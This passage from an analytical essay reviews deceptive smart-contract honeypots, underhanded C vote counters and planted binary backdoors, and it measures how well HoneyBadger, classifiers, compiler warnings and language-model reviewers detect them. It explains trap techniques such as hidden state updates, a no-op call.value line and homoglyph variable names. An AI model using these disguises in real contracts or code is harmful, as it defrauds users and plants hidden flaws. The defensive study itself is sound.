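| Inheritance disorder | 41 | 17 | 41% |
| Skip empty string literal | 9 | 7 | 78% |
| Type deduction overflow | 4 | 1 | 25% |
| Uninitialised struct | 32 | 11 | 34% |
| Hidden state update | 134 | 49 | 37% |
| Hidden transfer | 12 | 3 | 25% |
| Straw man contract | 30 | 8 | 27% |
| **All** | **282** | **103** | **37%** |

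The paper gives 33% for hidden transfer, but the counts in the slides work out to 25%. The compiler bug with the empty string did best, which is plausible because nothing in the source looks wrong. Hidden transfer did poorly, perhaps because readers only had to scroll to see the transfer. But both groups are small, and the honeypots also differed in how much bait they offered and what they promised.

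Of the other 179 honeypots, 151 were empty and had caught nobody, and 28 still held their bait. The successful honeypots caught 240 addresses in total. About 71% of these contracts caught only one victim, while one caught 97, or 40% of all victims. Torres and colleagues suggest that later users saw the failed attempts in the transaction history and stayed away. But most creators withdrew the money within a day of catching someone, which left little to attract a second victim.

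Victims came quickly, at a median of 16 hours after deployment. About 55% came within a day, and the fastest attempt took less than eight minutes. The average was nine days because a few honeypots caught no one for months, the longest for 142 days. Users left comments on the Etherscan pages of 87 honeypots, mostly to warn others. Only four of these honeypots caught their victims after a comment appeared, possibly because people read the warnings. The honeypots' age may also be a reason, since they seldom caught anyone after the first few days.

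Torres and colleagues labeled an address as an attacker if it created the honeypot, was the first to send it ether, or received more than it paid in. They labeled any other address as a victim if it paid in more than it received.

This rule can mislabel accounts in two ways. If a creator adds bait from a second account and withdraws it to the main one, the second account looks like a victim. If a reader beats the trap and takes the bait, the rule labels that reader as an attacker, and the honeypot may appear to have been abandoned. Ishimaki and Omote found that this had happened, mostly in honeypots that used hidden state updates. Some creators forgot to set the trap or did not know how, and users took their ether. Because the rule counts addresses, it can also count one person more than once.

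Torres and colleagues put the total profit at 257 ether, or $90,118 at the prices when the creators withdrew it. That is about $875 for each successful honeypot, and the most profitable one made $2,609. Ishimaki and Omote later examined the 323 contracts with available source code that HoneyBadger flagged, and found 177 losses totaling about 105 ether. Almost all of the difference comes from two techniques. Ishimaki and Omote counted losses of 60 ether from hidden state updates and 8 from straw man contracts, while Torres and colleagues reported profits of 171 and 47.

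The higher figures probably include money that did not come from victims. Dividing the total profit by the average gives about 119 profitable hidden state update contracts, of which only 49 caught anyone, and 27 profitable straw man contracts, of which only 8 did. Some creators may have deposited the bait from one account and withdrawn it to another, which would make their own money look like profit.

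### Thieves or players

The victims' intentions matter for judging how well readers spot disguised code. A victim who set out to rob a contract must have studied it to some extent, but one who joined a lottery may never have looked at the code.

Sherbachev treated the victims as would-be hackers. He objected to the name "honeypots" and preferred "mousetraps", because security teams use honeypots to detect attacks, while these contracts only take money from less skilled hackers. Torres and colleagues were less sure how to judge the creators or the users, since a creator might claim to be punishing thieves and a user might believe that a lottery was fair.

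Ishimaki and Omote studied 172 honeypots that used hidden state update, inheritance disorder or the empty string. They classified 124 as imitations of games and 48 as contracts that looked vulnerable. This suggests many victims could have been honest players. The count doesn't show how many were, and it leaves out five of the techniques.

It is often impossible to tell from transaction records whether a victim meant to cheat. In CryptoRoulette, an honest player and a cheat who has looked up the secret number both send 0.1 ether and a guess. In KingOfTheHill, paying more than the jackpot and then taking everything could be how the game is meant to work. Even Private_Bank, whose bait appeals to thieves, would trap an honest customer who only wanted to withdraw a deposit.

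RACEFORETH, another contract that dawu and 0x7F describe, needs no apparent flaw because players can lose money while following its rules exactly. Players win a prize once their payments add up to 100 finney (0.1 ether). The first payment can be at most 50 finney, and the limit halves after each payment. A player who always pays the maximum sends 50, 25, 12.5 and so on, so the total approaches 100 but never reaches it.

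### What skilled readers missed

Straw man contracts like Private_Bank provide the clearest evidence about skilled readers. To exploit reentrancy, a victim has to recognize the flaw, understand how the calls nest and write a contract that carries out the attack. Eight of the 30 straw man contracts caught someone, though some victims may have been ordinary depositors, and not every contract used reentrancy as bait. Victims with these skills had a strong reason to read carefully because their own money was at stake, but they did not check which contract was behind `Log`.

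They also had a reason to hurry, because only the first person to exploit a real flaw gets the money. Sherbachev called the duplicated variable in ICO_Hold easy for a hacker in a rush to miss. A programmer who reviews a patch or decides whether to trust an opponent's program may have more time, and would probably do better.

The 37% success rate is the share of honeypots that fooled at least one reader, whether that was the only reader or one in a thousand. Nobody recorded how many people read a honeypot, saw the trap and left. Ishimaki and Omote examined 112 failed honeypots and found several reasons for failure, including a lack of visitors and users who tested the contract with a payment of 0 ether, which cost them only the transaction fee. The figures therefore don't provide a detection rate. They also don't provide a false alarm rate, because nobody recorded how often the same readers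 avoided honest contracts.

Eight of the 240 victims' addresses lost ether to more than one honeypot, and one lost ether to four. The old contracts kept catching people after researchers had published the techniques. Ishimaki and Omote list six payments into honeypots in May 2022, worth just over 2 ether in total. One address paid 0.11 ether into an uninitialised struct honeypot, then 0.1 ether more about an hour and a half later. Five days after that, the same address tried a hidden state update honeypot, paying only 1 wei at a time. The next day a different address paid 1 ether into that honeypot, then slightly more than 1 ether six minutes later.

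## 2019 and 2020: the first measurements of automated detection

A published warning helps only people who read it before they pay. Torres and colleagues built HoneyBadger to recognize honeypots from their code. Most of the programs they ran it on, unlike the contest entries, were not deceptive, so the results also show how often the tool raised false alarms.

### How HoneyBadger works

HoneyBadger analyzes bytecode, so it does not need the source code. It uses symbolic execution, which runs a program with unknowns in place of actual inputs. At each decision in the program, the tool follows both branches and records the conditions for each. Software called a solver then checks whether the conditions along each path can all hold at once. If no input satisfies them, the path is infeasible, meaning the program can never take it.

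The analysis has three stages:

1. HoneyBadger explores the paths through a contract and collects every payment, every call to another contract and every change to stored data.
2. It discards any contract that cannot both receive and send ether. A honeypot has to do both, since it takes the victim's money and later pays its creator.
3. It applies eight rules to the remaining contracts, one for each known technique.

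The rule for balance disorder is the simplest to follow. It detects MultiplicatorX3, the contract that seems to give its balance to anyone who sends at least that much. Let b be the ether in the contract before a call, and p the user's payment.

1. Ethereum adds the payment before the code runs, so the balance during the call is b + p.
2. The contract pays out only if the payment is at least as large as the balance, so the condition for that path is p ≥ b + p.
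3. Subtracting p from both sides leaves 0 ≥ b. But the contract contains bait, so b is greater than 0 and the path is infeasible.
4. HoneyBadger follows the path anyway and finds an instruction that pays out the balance plus the user's payment.
5. The rule reports a balance disorder whenever a payment of this amount is on an infeasible path.

Symbolic execution tools usually save time by dropping infeasible paths, which can never run. In this honeypot, the bait is a payment on such a path, so a tool that dropped the path would find only a function that accepts ether and does nothing with it.

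Working from bytecode defeats some disguises. The compiler discards comments and spacing, so HoneyBadger processes code that a creator pushed off the edge of the screen like any other code. But the compiler also discards useful information. The source of KingOfTheHill shows that two related contracts both declare a variable called `owner`, while the bytecode has only numbered storage slots. HoneyBadger therefore detects inheritance disorder by looking for a contract that stores the caller's address in a slot it never checks and makes a payment depend on a different slot.

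### 460 suspects

Many Ethereum contracts are exact copies of others, so the 2 million that Torres and colleagues downloaded included only 151,935 with distinct bytecode. Of these, 48,487 could both receive and send ether. HoneyBadger took 31 seconds to analyze a typical contract, finished 98% of contracts within its 30-minute limit, and flagged 460 as honeypots.

Torres and colleagues found the source code for 323 of the 460 and checked by hand whether each contained the trap the tool had reported. They confirmed 282, a precision of 87%.

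| Technique | Flagged, with source | Confirmed | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Balance disorder | 20 | 20 | 100% |
| Inheritance disorder | 48 | 41 | 85% |
| Skip empty string literal | 9 | 9 | 100% |
| Type deduction overflow | 4 | 4 | 100% |
| Uninitialised struct | 32 | 32 | 100% |
| Hidden state update | 164 | 134 | 82% |
| Hidden transfer | 12 | 12 | 100% |
| Straw man contract | 34 | 30 | 88% |
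| **All** | **323** | **282** | **87%** |

Three rules caused all 41 mistakes. The rule for hidden state updates flags a contract if a payment depends on a stored value that another function can change without any transfer of ether. Honest contracts can also match, for example if the owner can pause withdrawals. One version of the straw man rule flags a contract that pays the caller and then passes the caller's address to a second contract. It doesn't examine the second contract, so it could flag a bank whose second contract is a harmless log.

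The manual check confirmed that a trap existed but could not show whether anyone had intended it, so a beginner who wrote MultiplicatorX3 by mistake would have been counted as the creator of a honeypot.

### Precision without a detection rate

Torres and colleagues report "false positive rates" of up to 18%, but these are shares of the flagged contracts. The share of honest contracts wrongly flagged was much lower. If HoneyBadger was wrong as often about the 137 flagged contracts without source code as about those with it, it raised about 58 false alarms. That is roughly one for every 2,600 honest contracts, or one for every 800 if we count only those that can receive and send ether.

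HoneyBadger's detection rate, or recall, is unknown. Calculating it would require counting the honeypots among the 151,475 contracts that the tool did not flag. If there were as many there as the tool had found, its recall would be 50%, while its precision would still be 87%. HoneyBadger flagged all 24 honeypots that Torres and colleagues had collected beforehand, but they had worked out the eight techniques from those same contracts. They describe their totals as a lower bound.

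The rules do handle variation within a technique. Two honeypots that both used hidden state updates could have bytecode that was only 11% similar, so a tool that searched for copies of known honeypots would have missed many. But a honeypot that uses a technique other than the eight covered will usually match none of the rules. Torres and colleagues acknowledge this and designed the tool so that others could add rules. Someone still has to discover each new technique, perhaps by losing money to it, before anyone can write a rule for it.

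### Scanners that took the bait

Most analysis tools for smart contracts look for real vulnerabilities, and the bait that deceives a thief can also lead them to report a honeypot as vulnerable. *Empirical Review of Automated Analysis Tools on 47,587 Ethereum Smart Contracts* (2019) compared nine tools, including HoneyBadger. HoneyBadger identified 19 contracts as honeypots baited with reentrancy, like Private_Bank. Three other tools reported 15 of these as vulnerable. Together the nine tools reported at least one problem in 93% of all the contracts, which suggests a very high false alarm rate.

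*EF/CF* (2023) describes a later fuzzer that tries to construct a working attack on a contract. Its developers tested it on reentrancy honeypots such as Private_Bank, which secretly calls a different contract from the one in the published file. When the fuzzer had only the published source, it set up a fresh copy and found an attack that worked on that copy. When the developers also gave it the contract's stored data and the outside contract from the blockchain, it correctly reported no attack.

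Honeypots have also distorted the collections of contracts used to test detection tools. *EF/CF* found that in one widely used collection, 19 of the 31 contracts labeled as vulnerable to reentrancy were honeypots. A tool that wrongly reported all 19 as vulnerable would get a good score. Di Angelo, Ferreira and colleagues (2023), in *Evolution of Automated Weakness Detection in Ethereum Bytecode*, ran 12 tools on 248,328 contracts but did not try to calculate error rates, because they thought no existing set of contracts with known answers was large, consistent and balanced enough. They also found that the tools performed worse, to varying degrees, as Ethereum changed, so a detection rate from 2019 might no longer hold even if nobody had tried to evade the tool.

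### A classifier that follows the money

Camino and colleagues, who included HoneyBadger's developers, tried to detect honeypots without giving the detector a description of any honeypot technique. They trained a machine learning model on contracts that Torres and colleagues had confirmed as honeypots and exact copies of those contracts, 295 in total. The other 158,568 contracts with published source code served as examples of ordinary contracts. The model combined many small decision trees, each correcting errors left by the previous ones.

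It used three kinds of information:

- **Source code:** the number of lines and the compiler version, among other things, but not what the code does.
- **Transactions:** how many there were, how much ether they carried and how far apart they came.
- **Flow of funds:** who sent each transaction, and whether the balances of the creator, the contract and the sender went up or down.

The most informative feature by far was a deposit from the creator into the contract, which is how most creators place the bait. Honeypots that exploit a compiler bug have little code in common with those that exploit a gap in Etherscan's transaction list, but their creators handle money in similar ways.

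On contracts held back from training, the model had an AUROC of 0.968, which is the probability that it ranks a randomly chosen honeypot above a randomly chosen ordinary contract. Honeypots were so rare that even a score this high does not guarantee good precision. A detector that caught all 295 honeypots and wrongly flagged 1% of the other contracts would raise about 1,600 false alarms, so its precision would be only 16%. If half of all contracts were honeypots, the same detector would have a precision of 99%. For the same reason, HoneyBadger's 87% precision is weak evidence of the precision to expect where disguised programs are more or less common than they were on Ethereum.

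To simulate a new technique, Camino and colleagues removed one technique at a time from the training data and tested the model on the honeypots that used it. The model detected 269 of the 295 honeypots (91%). Detection rates ranged from 17 out of 20 for balance disorder to 4 out of 4 for type deduction overflow.

These tests contained only honeypots, so they can't measure the false alarm rate, and a model that flagged everything would have scored 100%. The removed techniques were new only in their code, since their creators still deposited bait and waited for someone to pay. A creator who knew about the model could change this pattern by placing the bait from a second account.

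Camino and colleagues then ranked the contracts that Torres and colleagues had not confirmed as honeypots, and read the top 100. They found 57 more honeypots, 50 of which used techniques HoneyBadger already had rules for. Among contracts with published source, HoneyBadger had therefore caught at most about 85% of the honeypots its rules were meant to cover. The true figure is probably lower, because nobody read past the first 100. All 12 contracts the tool flagged for hidden transfers were honeypots, but Camino and colleagues found eight more that it had missed, so its detection rate for that technique was at most about 60%.

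The other seven honeypots used two new techniques. Six relied on a missing pair of parentheses:

```solidity
msg.sender.call.value(amount)();    // sends the ether
msg.sender.call.value(amount);      // prepares a payment, never sends it
```

In old versions of Solidity, the second line was legal and did nothing. Most versions of the compiler removed it, so the bytecode contained no trace of the payment that had attracted the victim. HoneyBadger keeps infeasible paths to find bait that can never pay out, but this bait existed only in the source code.

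The seventh honeypot stores its owner's address under the name "Stephen", and a function that anyone can pay to call seems to replace the owner. In that function, the second "e" in the name is a Cyrillic letter that looks the same, so the contract stores the new address under a different name and the original owner keeps control.

### Deciding before anyone has paid

Camino and colleagues point out that the transaction features are useless for a contract that has no transactions yet. An Ethereum user may at least be able to see the creator's deposit, but some of the other evidence comes from people who have already paid. A one-shot program game provides no such evidence, because each program must choose its move before the other has acted. When Camino and colleagues gave the model only the source code features, it still scored 0.942, but it relied mainly on file length and compiler version,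 both of which an author can easily change.

Later detectors based on behavior have similar gaps. *Why Trick Me* (2023) describes a method that looks for tokens people can buy but not sell by simulating trades and examining past ones. The method can detect a delayed trap only after somebody has switched it on, and it misses some other kinds until they have at least one victim. The detector in *Pump-and-Dump meets Honeypot Tokens* (2026) misses contracts whose code for blocking trades has never run. Flagging all such code would catch these contracts, but also those of honest developers who keep trading closed until an advance sale ends.

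HoneyBadger needs only the bytecode, so it can check a contract before it has any victims. Torres, Baden and State built a plugin for MetaMask, a popular Ethereum wallet, and described it in *Towards Usable Protection Against Honeypots*. Their server runs HoneyBadger on each new contract. When a user is about to send money, the plugin checks the result and displays a warning or an approval. If HoneyBadger has no rule for a honeypot's technique, the user will probably see an approval, which may be worse than no message.

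### Five countermeasures and 40 vote counters

Wheeler instead studied detection using programs that were all supposed to cheat, the entries from Horn's 2004 vote-counting contest. He did this work for the Institute for Defense Analyses, a nonprofit that runs research centers for the US government. He excluded one entry because its published file contained no attack, which left 40.

Even finding the malicious lines took work, because some of the organizers' explanations were wrong or incomplete. Travis Fisher's entry, for example, had harmless source code. The attack was in the compile command, which redefined a standard test for blank spaces as a test for the letter K, and the contest page had omitted that command.

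Wheeler then chose five simple countermeasures and worked out which entries each would expose. Some entries count more than once:

| Countermeasure | Entries exposed |
|---|---|
| Run the program with a tool that detects misuse of memory | 5 |
| Allow macros only where nothing else will do | 9 |
| Ban the names `l` and `O`, which look like digits | 8 |
| Color the code, and reformat it so that no code can follow a comment on the same line | 2 |
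| Compile with many of gcc's warnings switched on | 15 |
| **At least one of the five** | **30** |

The total of 30 out of 40, or 75%, is partly a prediction. Wheeler ran gcc on every entry, and it exposed 15. He did not run the memory tool on all of them, and the tool for banning confusing names did not exist. The other 15 therefore depend on his judgment of what those tools would have exposed.

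The memory tool also works only while a program is running, so it would miss the overflow in Parkanzky's entry unless the program ran on election day. The compiler gcc caught this entry from its source code alone, warning that the message might not fit. It also caught Zalewski's entry, warning that one variable hid another of the same name. These were the two winning entries, so a compiler easily found the disguises the judges had considered best.

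Ten entries escaped. One should have triggered gcc's warning about misleading indentation, but a bug in gcc suppressed it. Wheeler thought six others would make a reviewer suspicious, including one that came with an obviously scrambled script. That left three that were neither caught nor suspicious:

- **Matthew Russotto** used a table, `Tallymap`, to look up which total each letter adds to. A loop seems to fill in the whole table, but it stops at the size of a different and much smaller table called `Tally`. The remaining letters keep a wrong starting value, so votes for minor candidates can go to the wrong total.
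- **Robert Seace** passed the list of totals to a function without saying what type of numbers it contained. The function then treats the list as single bytes, although each total takes up several, so it changes parts of totals instead of whole ones. Åkesson's warhead program later used a similar mismatch. Gcc did warn about this line, but only about a harmless conversion in its first half.
- **Jared Sohn** wrote `(Vote == 'n') || (Vote == 'n')`, which checks for a small n twice and never for a capital N. Votes for Nader therefore count as "Other".

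The judges gave these entries 5.3, 4.3 and 3.7 out of 10, well below the two winners. Sohn's repeated letter is a typing error that a careful person could spot, yet none of the five countermeasures caught it. People and tools evidently miss different things, so using both should catch more than using either alone. All three programs also cheat every day, so ordinary tests could have exposed them.

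### How much the 75% is worth

Wheeler found the result encouraging. More than half of the entries used one of five familiar kinds of trick, and he suggested new compiler warnings that could catch the three that got through. He also argued that underhanded code is hard to write because it must do a specific wrong thing while appearing to do the right one, and each countermeasure removes some of the ways to do both. In his view, defenses don't have to be perfect if they make discovery likely enough to deter attackers.

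He also noticed that the tricks became easier to find as he read more of them, and suggested training reviewers on such samples. This is weak evidence that training helps because, as he pointed out, the list ran from the hardest entries to the easiest.

Wheeler anticipated the objection that his test was unfair because he had studied the attacks before choosing the countermeasures. He replied that he only wanted to show that a small set of simple, general countermeasures can often detect underhanded code. The experiment supports that claim, but it doesn't show how many new programs the same five would catch, because he chose them to fit these 40. To find out, he would have had to test the same list, unchanged, on another contest's entries.

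A second problem is that the entrants were writing for human judges and had no reason to evade these measures. An author who expects gcc's warnings can switch them on and revise the program until they stop. This seems feasible, since all the entries that the Underhanded C Contest's judges published in 2007 survived compiler warnings. Two of Horn's entrants wrote `=` for `==`, and gcc caught both, though it would have missed the version with parentheses in the 2003 kernel attack.

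Wheeler's answer to such attackers was to publish some countermeasures and keep the details of others secret, so that nobody could be sure they had passed them all. A company can do this with its own code reviews, but it is harder in a program game, where the opponent can read the program's checks.

Wheeler did not test any honest programs, so his study provides no false alarm rate. He counted a gcc warning only if it pointed to the malicious line, but gcc also flagged many ordinary mistakes in the same programs. A reviewer who did not know which line was malicious would have to investigate every warning. Wheeler cites Les Hatton, who applied a well-known set of C coding rules to real programs and found that far too many of the violations were harmless.

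In the Prisoner's Dilemma described earlier, a reader that catches 75% of disguised programs makes disguise unprofitable as long as it wrongly flags no more than half of honest ones. A reader that rejected every program that broke one of Wheeler's measures might flag more than half, because honest C programmers often use macros and many of their programs produce compiler warnings.

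## Language models searching for planted backdoors

Wheeler's countermeasures and HoneyBadger's rules look for known patterns and can't determine whether code makes sense for the program's purpose. Language models might do better because they process comments and variable names along with the instructions. A model could flag an error check as serving no purpose, as readers did with the two lines in the Linux kernel. But reassuring comments could also mislead a model, as they do people.

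### Why the contest entries make a weak test

Nobody appears to have published a systematic test of language models on entries from the underhanded contests. The closest study, *Large Language Models for Code Analysis* (2023), used entries from a contest for openly obfuscated C programs. GPT-4 recognized 22 of the samples as contest code, which suggests its training data included them or pages about them.

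Models may also have memorized the published underhanded entries. Organizers usually posted the winning programs with an explanation of the trick, and programmers have discussed them online ever since. A model could therefore identify the leak in Meacham's redaction program by recalling the contest page, without working through the loop. Horn's incorrect explanations might help detect some of this memorization. If a model attributes the miscounting in Cumings's entry to the swapped letter O and doesn't mention `vote % 2`, it is probably repeating Horn's page. A correct answer would be weak evidence of analysis, because Wheeler's corrections are online too.

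A fair test needs programs that are newer than the model. *MalTotal* (2026), a study of malicious software packages, describes taking this precaution with some of its test packages, which appeared only after the release of DeepSeek-V3 and GPT-4o, two of the models in the study. Even the entries from the 2024 Solidity contest are too old for such a test of the leading models of 2026. The test would also need honest programs written for the same tasks, to measure false alarms.

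### Noticing, locating and predicting

Existing tests mix three abilities: noticing that something is odd, locating the trick, and predicting what the program will do. The `find` program, which defects only if the opponent's text begins with `def `, shows how these abilities differ. One reader might sense that something is wrong but be unable to say what. Another might point to the `if` line but still wrongly predict that the program will defect against an empty file.

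Underhanded code mainly tests a reader's ability to predict what a program will do. Contestants remove whatever looks odd, and in the best entries a reader sees the trick but misunderstands it. A player in a program game also has to predict the opponent's move. Noticing odd code is still useful because a reader can refuse to trust it, but that policy also rejects harmless programs that are merely unusual.

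### Backdoors in compiled programs

The BinaryAudit benchmark mainly tests whether language models can locate backdoors. In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) describe how they added backdoors by hand to four open-source network programs and gave the models only the compiled programs. The models could use Ghidra and Radare2, tools that translate machine code into something closer to C. In most of the backdoor tasks, a model passes only if it gives the address of the function that contains the backdoor. Other tasks use clean programs, and the correct answer is that there is no backdoor.

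In February 2026, Claude Opus 4.6 found 49% of the backdoors, the most of any model tested, although a skilled human could have found them fairly easily. On clean programs, the models reported nonexistent problems 28% of the time. Grabowski and colleagues think a practical tool would need a false alarm rate below 0.001%, because most software is safe.

The current ranking in Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?* covers 26 models. None is newer than March 2026, so the strongest models of late 2026 are missing. The table lists the top results for which both rates are available. Its last column uses the Prisoner's Dilemma formula (1 + f)/2 to give the detection rate at which disguise stops being worthwhile.

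| Model | Detection rate | False alarm rate | Detection rate needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 49% | 25% | 63% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 49% | 17% | 58% |
| GPT-5.2-Codex, highest effort | 46% | 0% | 50% |

None of the three reaches the required rate. GPT-5.2-Codex comes closest because it raised no false alarms. It also leads when the score includes the clean programs and the tests of tool use, with 69% according to Quesma's *BinaryAudit / gpt-5.2-codex-xhigh*. The detection rates are probably a little too low for this purpose, since a model that reports a backdoor at the wrong address fails the task even though it would have refused to trust the program. But the backdoors were simple, while the formula applies to the best disguise an author can devise.

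Models scored much higher when they used more computation. GPT-5.2-Codex went from 9% at its ordinary setting to 46% at its highest, and GPT-5.4 went from 2% to 18%. A low score may therefore show only that a model stopped searching too early.

Results for individual tasks, which a model normally attempted three times each, are more informative than the averages. According to Quesma's *BinaryAudit / gemini-3.1-pro-preview*, Gemini 3.1 Pro found the backdoor in 21 of 24 attempts on dnsmasq, a program that manages addresses on a network, but in none of nine attempts on Dropbear, a program for remote logins. Judging by the task names, the Dropbear backdoor was a broken login check. A backdoor that runs an attacker's commands has to call a function to do so, which a model can search for, but a broken login check may contain nothing unusual to search for, so it is closer to underhanded code.

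Opus 4.6 did better on Dropbear, succeeding in four of nine attempts. But according to Quesma's *BinaryAudit/claude-opus-4.6*, it passed only one of its six attempts on clean copies of the same program, so its reports of a backdoor in Dropbear were weak evidence that one existed.

### Finding the code and excusing it

One of the dnsmasq failures shows the difference between the three abilities. Grabowski and colleagues added seven lines that take a command from a network message and run it. Opus 4.6 found `/bin/sh`, the name of the standard command interpreter, and traced it to the function with the backdoor. It found the instruction that runs the command, but concluded that this was probably how dnsmasq normally runs scripts. It then moved on to other functions without checking where the command came from.

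The model identified the right clue and located the right code but made the wrong prediction. dnsmasq does run scripts in some circumstances, so an innocent explanation was available, and people who write underhanded code supply such explanations on purpose.

An earlier model, Claude Opus 4.5, found a similar backdoor in the web server lighttpd within five minutes. It listed the functions that each file used, saw one that runs commands, and traced the call to a function named `li_check_debug_header`. The model called this a classic backdoor pattern, then read the translated code and correctly worked out that the server ran whatever command a visitor put in a certain header. It did predict the behavior here, but it knew where to look because of a suspicious function call and a revealing name.

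The same clues cause false alarms. Gemini 3 Pro reported that one of the clean servers would run a numerical setting as a command, but the program checks that the setting is a number and never runs it. *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (2026) found a similar pattern in 13 models, which often flagged ordinary network requests and file writes because malware uses them too, and ignored the surrounding program's purpose. A reviewer that relies on these clues will reject some clean programs and accept underhanded ones that avoid them.

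### Obfuscated code

Several studies tested how well models could analyze openly obfuscated code. In *Benchmarking Large Language Models for IoC Recovery under Adversarial Code Obfuscation*, Morales, Pastrana and Tapiador (2026) put an internet address into 336 JavaScript programs and concealed it in 12 increasingly elaborate ways. They asked five commercial models whether each program contained an address and, if so, which one. The models, which included GPT-4 Turbo and Claude 3 Sonnet, were already old.

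Four of the five models found the address every time when Morales and colleagues had only encoded it in Base64, renamed variables, added useless code or rearranged the program. When they encrypted the address, the models almost never found it, even though the program included the key and the decryption routine. The prompt asked for a bare answer in a fixed format, which left little room to work through a calculation. A model that could run the decryption routine would probably have done much better.

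Every version of every program contained an address, so this test cannot measure a false alarm rate. It also measures whether a model can recover a piece of data, not whether it can predict behavior. A reader can reject a program just because part of it is encrypted.

Böke and Torka (2025), in *Digital Camouflage*, did measure false alarms. They took 20 C functions with ordinary security flaws and 20 without, and used a compiler tool to produce obfuscated versions. Three models had to call each function secure or insecure:

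| Model | Detection, original | Detection, obfuscated | False alarms, original | False alarms, obfuscated |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT-4o | 85% | 80% | 25% | 75% |
| Gemini Flash 2.5 | 75% | 80% | 40% | 65% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 70% | 90% | 40% | 70% |

Obfuscation made the models flag most functions as flawed, including the secure ones, but it did not make them miss many more flaws. Each group had only 20 functions, so one answer changes a rate by five percentage points, but false alarms rose by much more than that.

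Claude Sonnet 4 would detect enough disguised programs to make disguise unprofitable in the Prisoner's Dilemma. With its false alarm rate of 70%, it needs to detect 85% of them, and it detected 90%. But it would also refuse to cooperate with most honest programs, which would score only 1.6 on average against it, compared with 3 for reliable cooperation and 1 for mutual defection.

A smaller study, *Deconstructing Obfuscation* (2025), tested whether eight commercial models could deobfuscate one short C program after the same kind of compiler obfuscation. Some obfuscation methods defeated all eight.

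The only test involving Trojan Source's invisible characters is an informal, undated trial. In *Trojan War against State-of-the-Art LLMs*, devansh asked more than ten models to predict the output of a short Python program in which these characters hid an early exit. Only Grok answered correctly. Unlike most of the other tests, this one asked models to predict a program's behavior, but it used one program, old models and a prompt that forbade any explanation, so its results don't indicate how current models would perform.

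### Disguised changes to real projects

The closest evidence on underhanded code comes from tests in which models review harmful changes to ordinary software projects. In *PRWeaver*, Wang, Cheng and Xie (2026) used a language model to write 208 attacks, which they planted in ten real projects, nearly all in Python. They confirmed that each attack worked and that the project's relevant tests still passed, and two people checked that the changes looked plausible.

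Six combinations of a review tool and a language model then examined the changes. A detection counted only if the report identified what the attack made possible. When the whole attack arrived as one change, detection ranged from 42% for OpenCodeReview with DeepSeek V4 Flash to 79% for Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6. Even with the same model, Claude Haiku 4.5, detection was 56%, 61% or 67%, depending on which of three tools ran it.

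The reviewers caught a smaller share of attacks when they also had to review harmless work. In the hardest condition, where the model saw the attack along with a large amount of ordinary code, three of the combinations found only 16% to 22% of attacks. The contest entries were short, so they did not have a large amount of ordinary code to hide an attack in.

Wang and colleagues did not report a false alarm rate, but we can calculate from the detection rates how low it would have to be to deter disguise. A reader that catches 79% of disguised programs makes disguise unprofitable if it flags no more than 58% of honest ones, but a 42% detection rate is too low even with no false alarms.

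One missed attack resembles the dnsmasq case. The attack weakened a "trust this browser" feature in two places, so that a stolen login cookie would keep working after the user changed the password. The reviewer described both changes correctly but failed to work out what they did together. It treated them as deliberate trade-offs between security and convenience and raised no objection.

The best contest entries make readers misunderstand the code itself. To understand Richards's exchange, a reader had to know that Solidity evaluates some values in a log entry from right to left. PRWeaver instead measures whether a model recognizes harm in code it has read correctly, and provides little evidence about whether the model would misread a line like that one.

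### Rejecting a change for the wrong reason

A reviewer can also reject a harmful change without having understood it. Chen, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Verdict to Diagnosis*, compared CodeRabbit, a widely used commercial reviewer, with PRGuard, a system of their own that first proposes a specific flaw and then looks for evidence of it in the project. PRGuard ran on the model DeepSeek v4-pro. Both reviewed the same 31 harmful changes:

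| Kind of flaw | Changes | CodeRabbit: blocked | CodeRabbit: named the flaw | PRGuard: blocked | PRGuard: named the flaw |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful code is present | 17 | 15 | 13 | 13 | 13 |
| A necessary check is missing | 14 | 9 | 3 | 9 | 9 |
| **All** | **31** | **24** | **16** | **22** | **22** |

CodeRabbit blocked slightly more changes but named the real flaw in fewer. The gap was largest when the flaw was an omission, which is harder to point to. CodeRabbit named none of the seven flaws that required evidence from files outside the change. Åkesson's warhead program relied on both difficulties, because its flaw was a missing line and a reader had to compare two files to see why it mattered.

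Rejecting a backdoored change for the wrong reason is dangerous for a project, because the author can fix the irrelevant problem and resubmit the change with the real flaw intact. In a one-shot program game, such a rejection would still protect the reader. But a reader that rejects disguised programs for irrelevant reasons will probably reject honest ones for the same reasons, so the false alarm rate is especially important there.

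Chen and colleagues tested PRGuard on 63 harmful changes and 50 harmless ones. With DeepSeek, it blocked 78% of the harmful changes and 8% of the harmless ones; with GPT-5.5, it blocked 68% and 10%. Disguise would no longer be worthwhile at detection rates of 54% and 55%, respectively, and both versions are well above these thresholds.

Most of the flaws were not disguised, which makes that result less encouraging. Chen and colleagues made many of the harmful changes by undoing part of a real security fix. In 37 of the 63, the change removed a protection in plain view, and both versions of PRGuard named the flaw every time. Seven others left out one necessary part of a fix, so no removal was visible, and each version named the flaw in only three of them. Of these seven harmful changes, the GPT-5.5 version blocked four, and it also blocked two of their seven harmless counterparts, which is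 below the required rate. Seven cases are too few for a firm conclusion, but they suggest that the overall figures depend heavily on how visible the flaws were.

### Flaws that nobody disguised

Models have become good at finding accidental flaws in real software. Chen and colleagues used PRGuard to find 12 undisclosed flaws in five widely used projects, and demonstrated a working attack for each. The UK's AI Security Institute found GPT-5.5 comparable to Anthropic's Claude Mythos at finding security flaws, according to Schneier on Security's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.5 is as Good as Mythos at Finding Security Vulnerabilities* (2026). Epoch AI's *Are Mythos’ cyber capabilities overhyped?* (2026) reviewed the public evidence on the first version of Mythos and found that it was a real jump in the ability to exploit flaws, but that the practical gain in finding them was unclear.

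Some of this skill should carry over to underhanded code, which often imitates common mistakes. Parkanzky's vote counter, for example, has an overflow because it reserves too little memory. C programmers often make this mistake, so a model that has learned to recognize it has a good chance of finding the overflow, which gcc also caught.

A model is likely to find accidental flaws more often than disguised flaws of the same technical difficulty, because accidental flaws were not designed to get past a reader. Someone who disguises a flaw may put it in an inconspicuous place or write a comment to explain it away. They have usually also tried to read the code as a reviewer would and discarded versions that looked suspicious.

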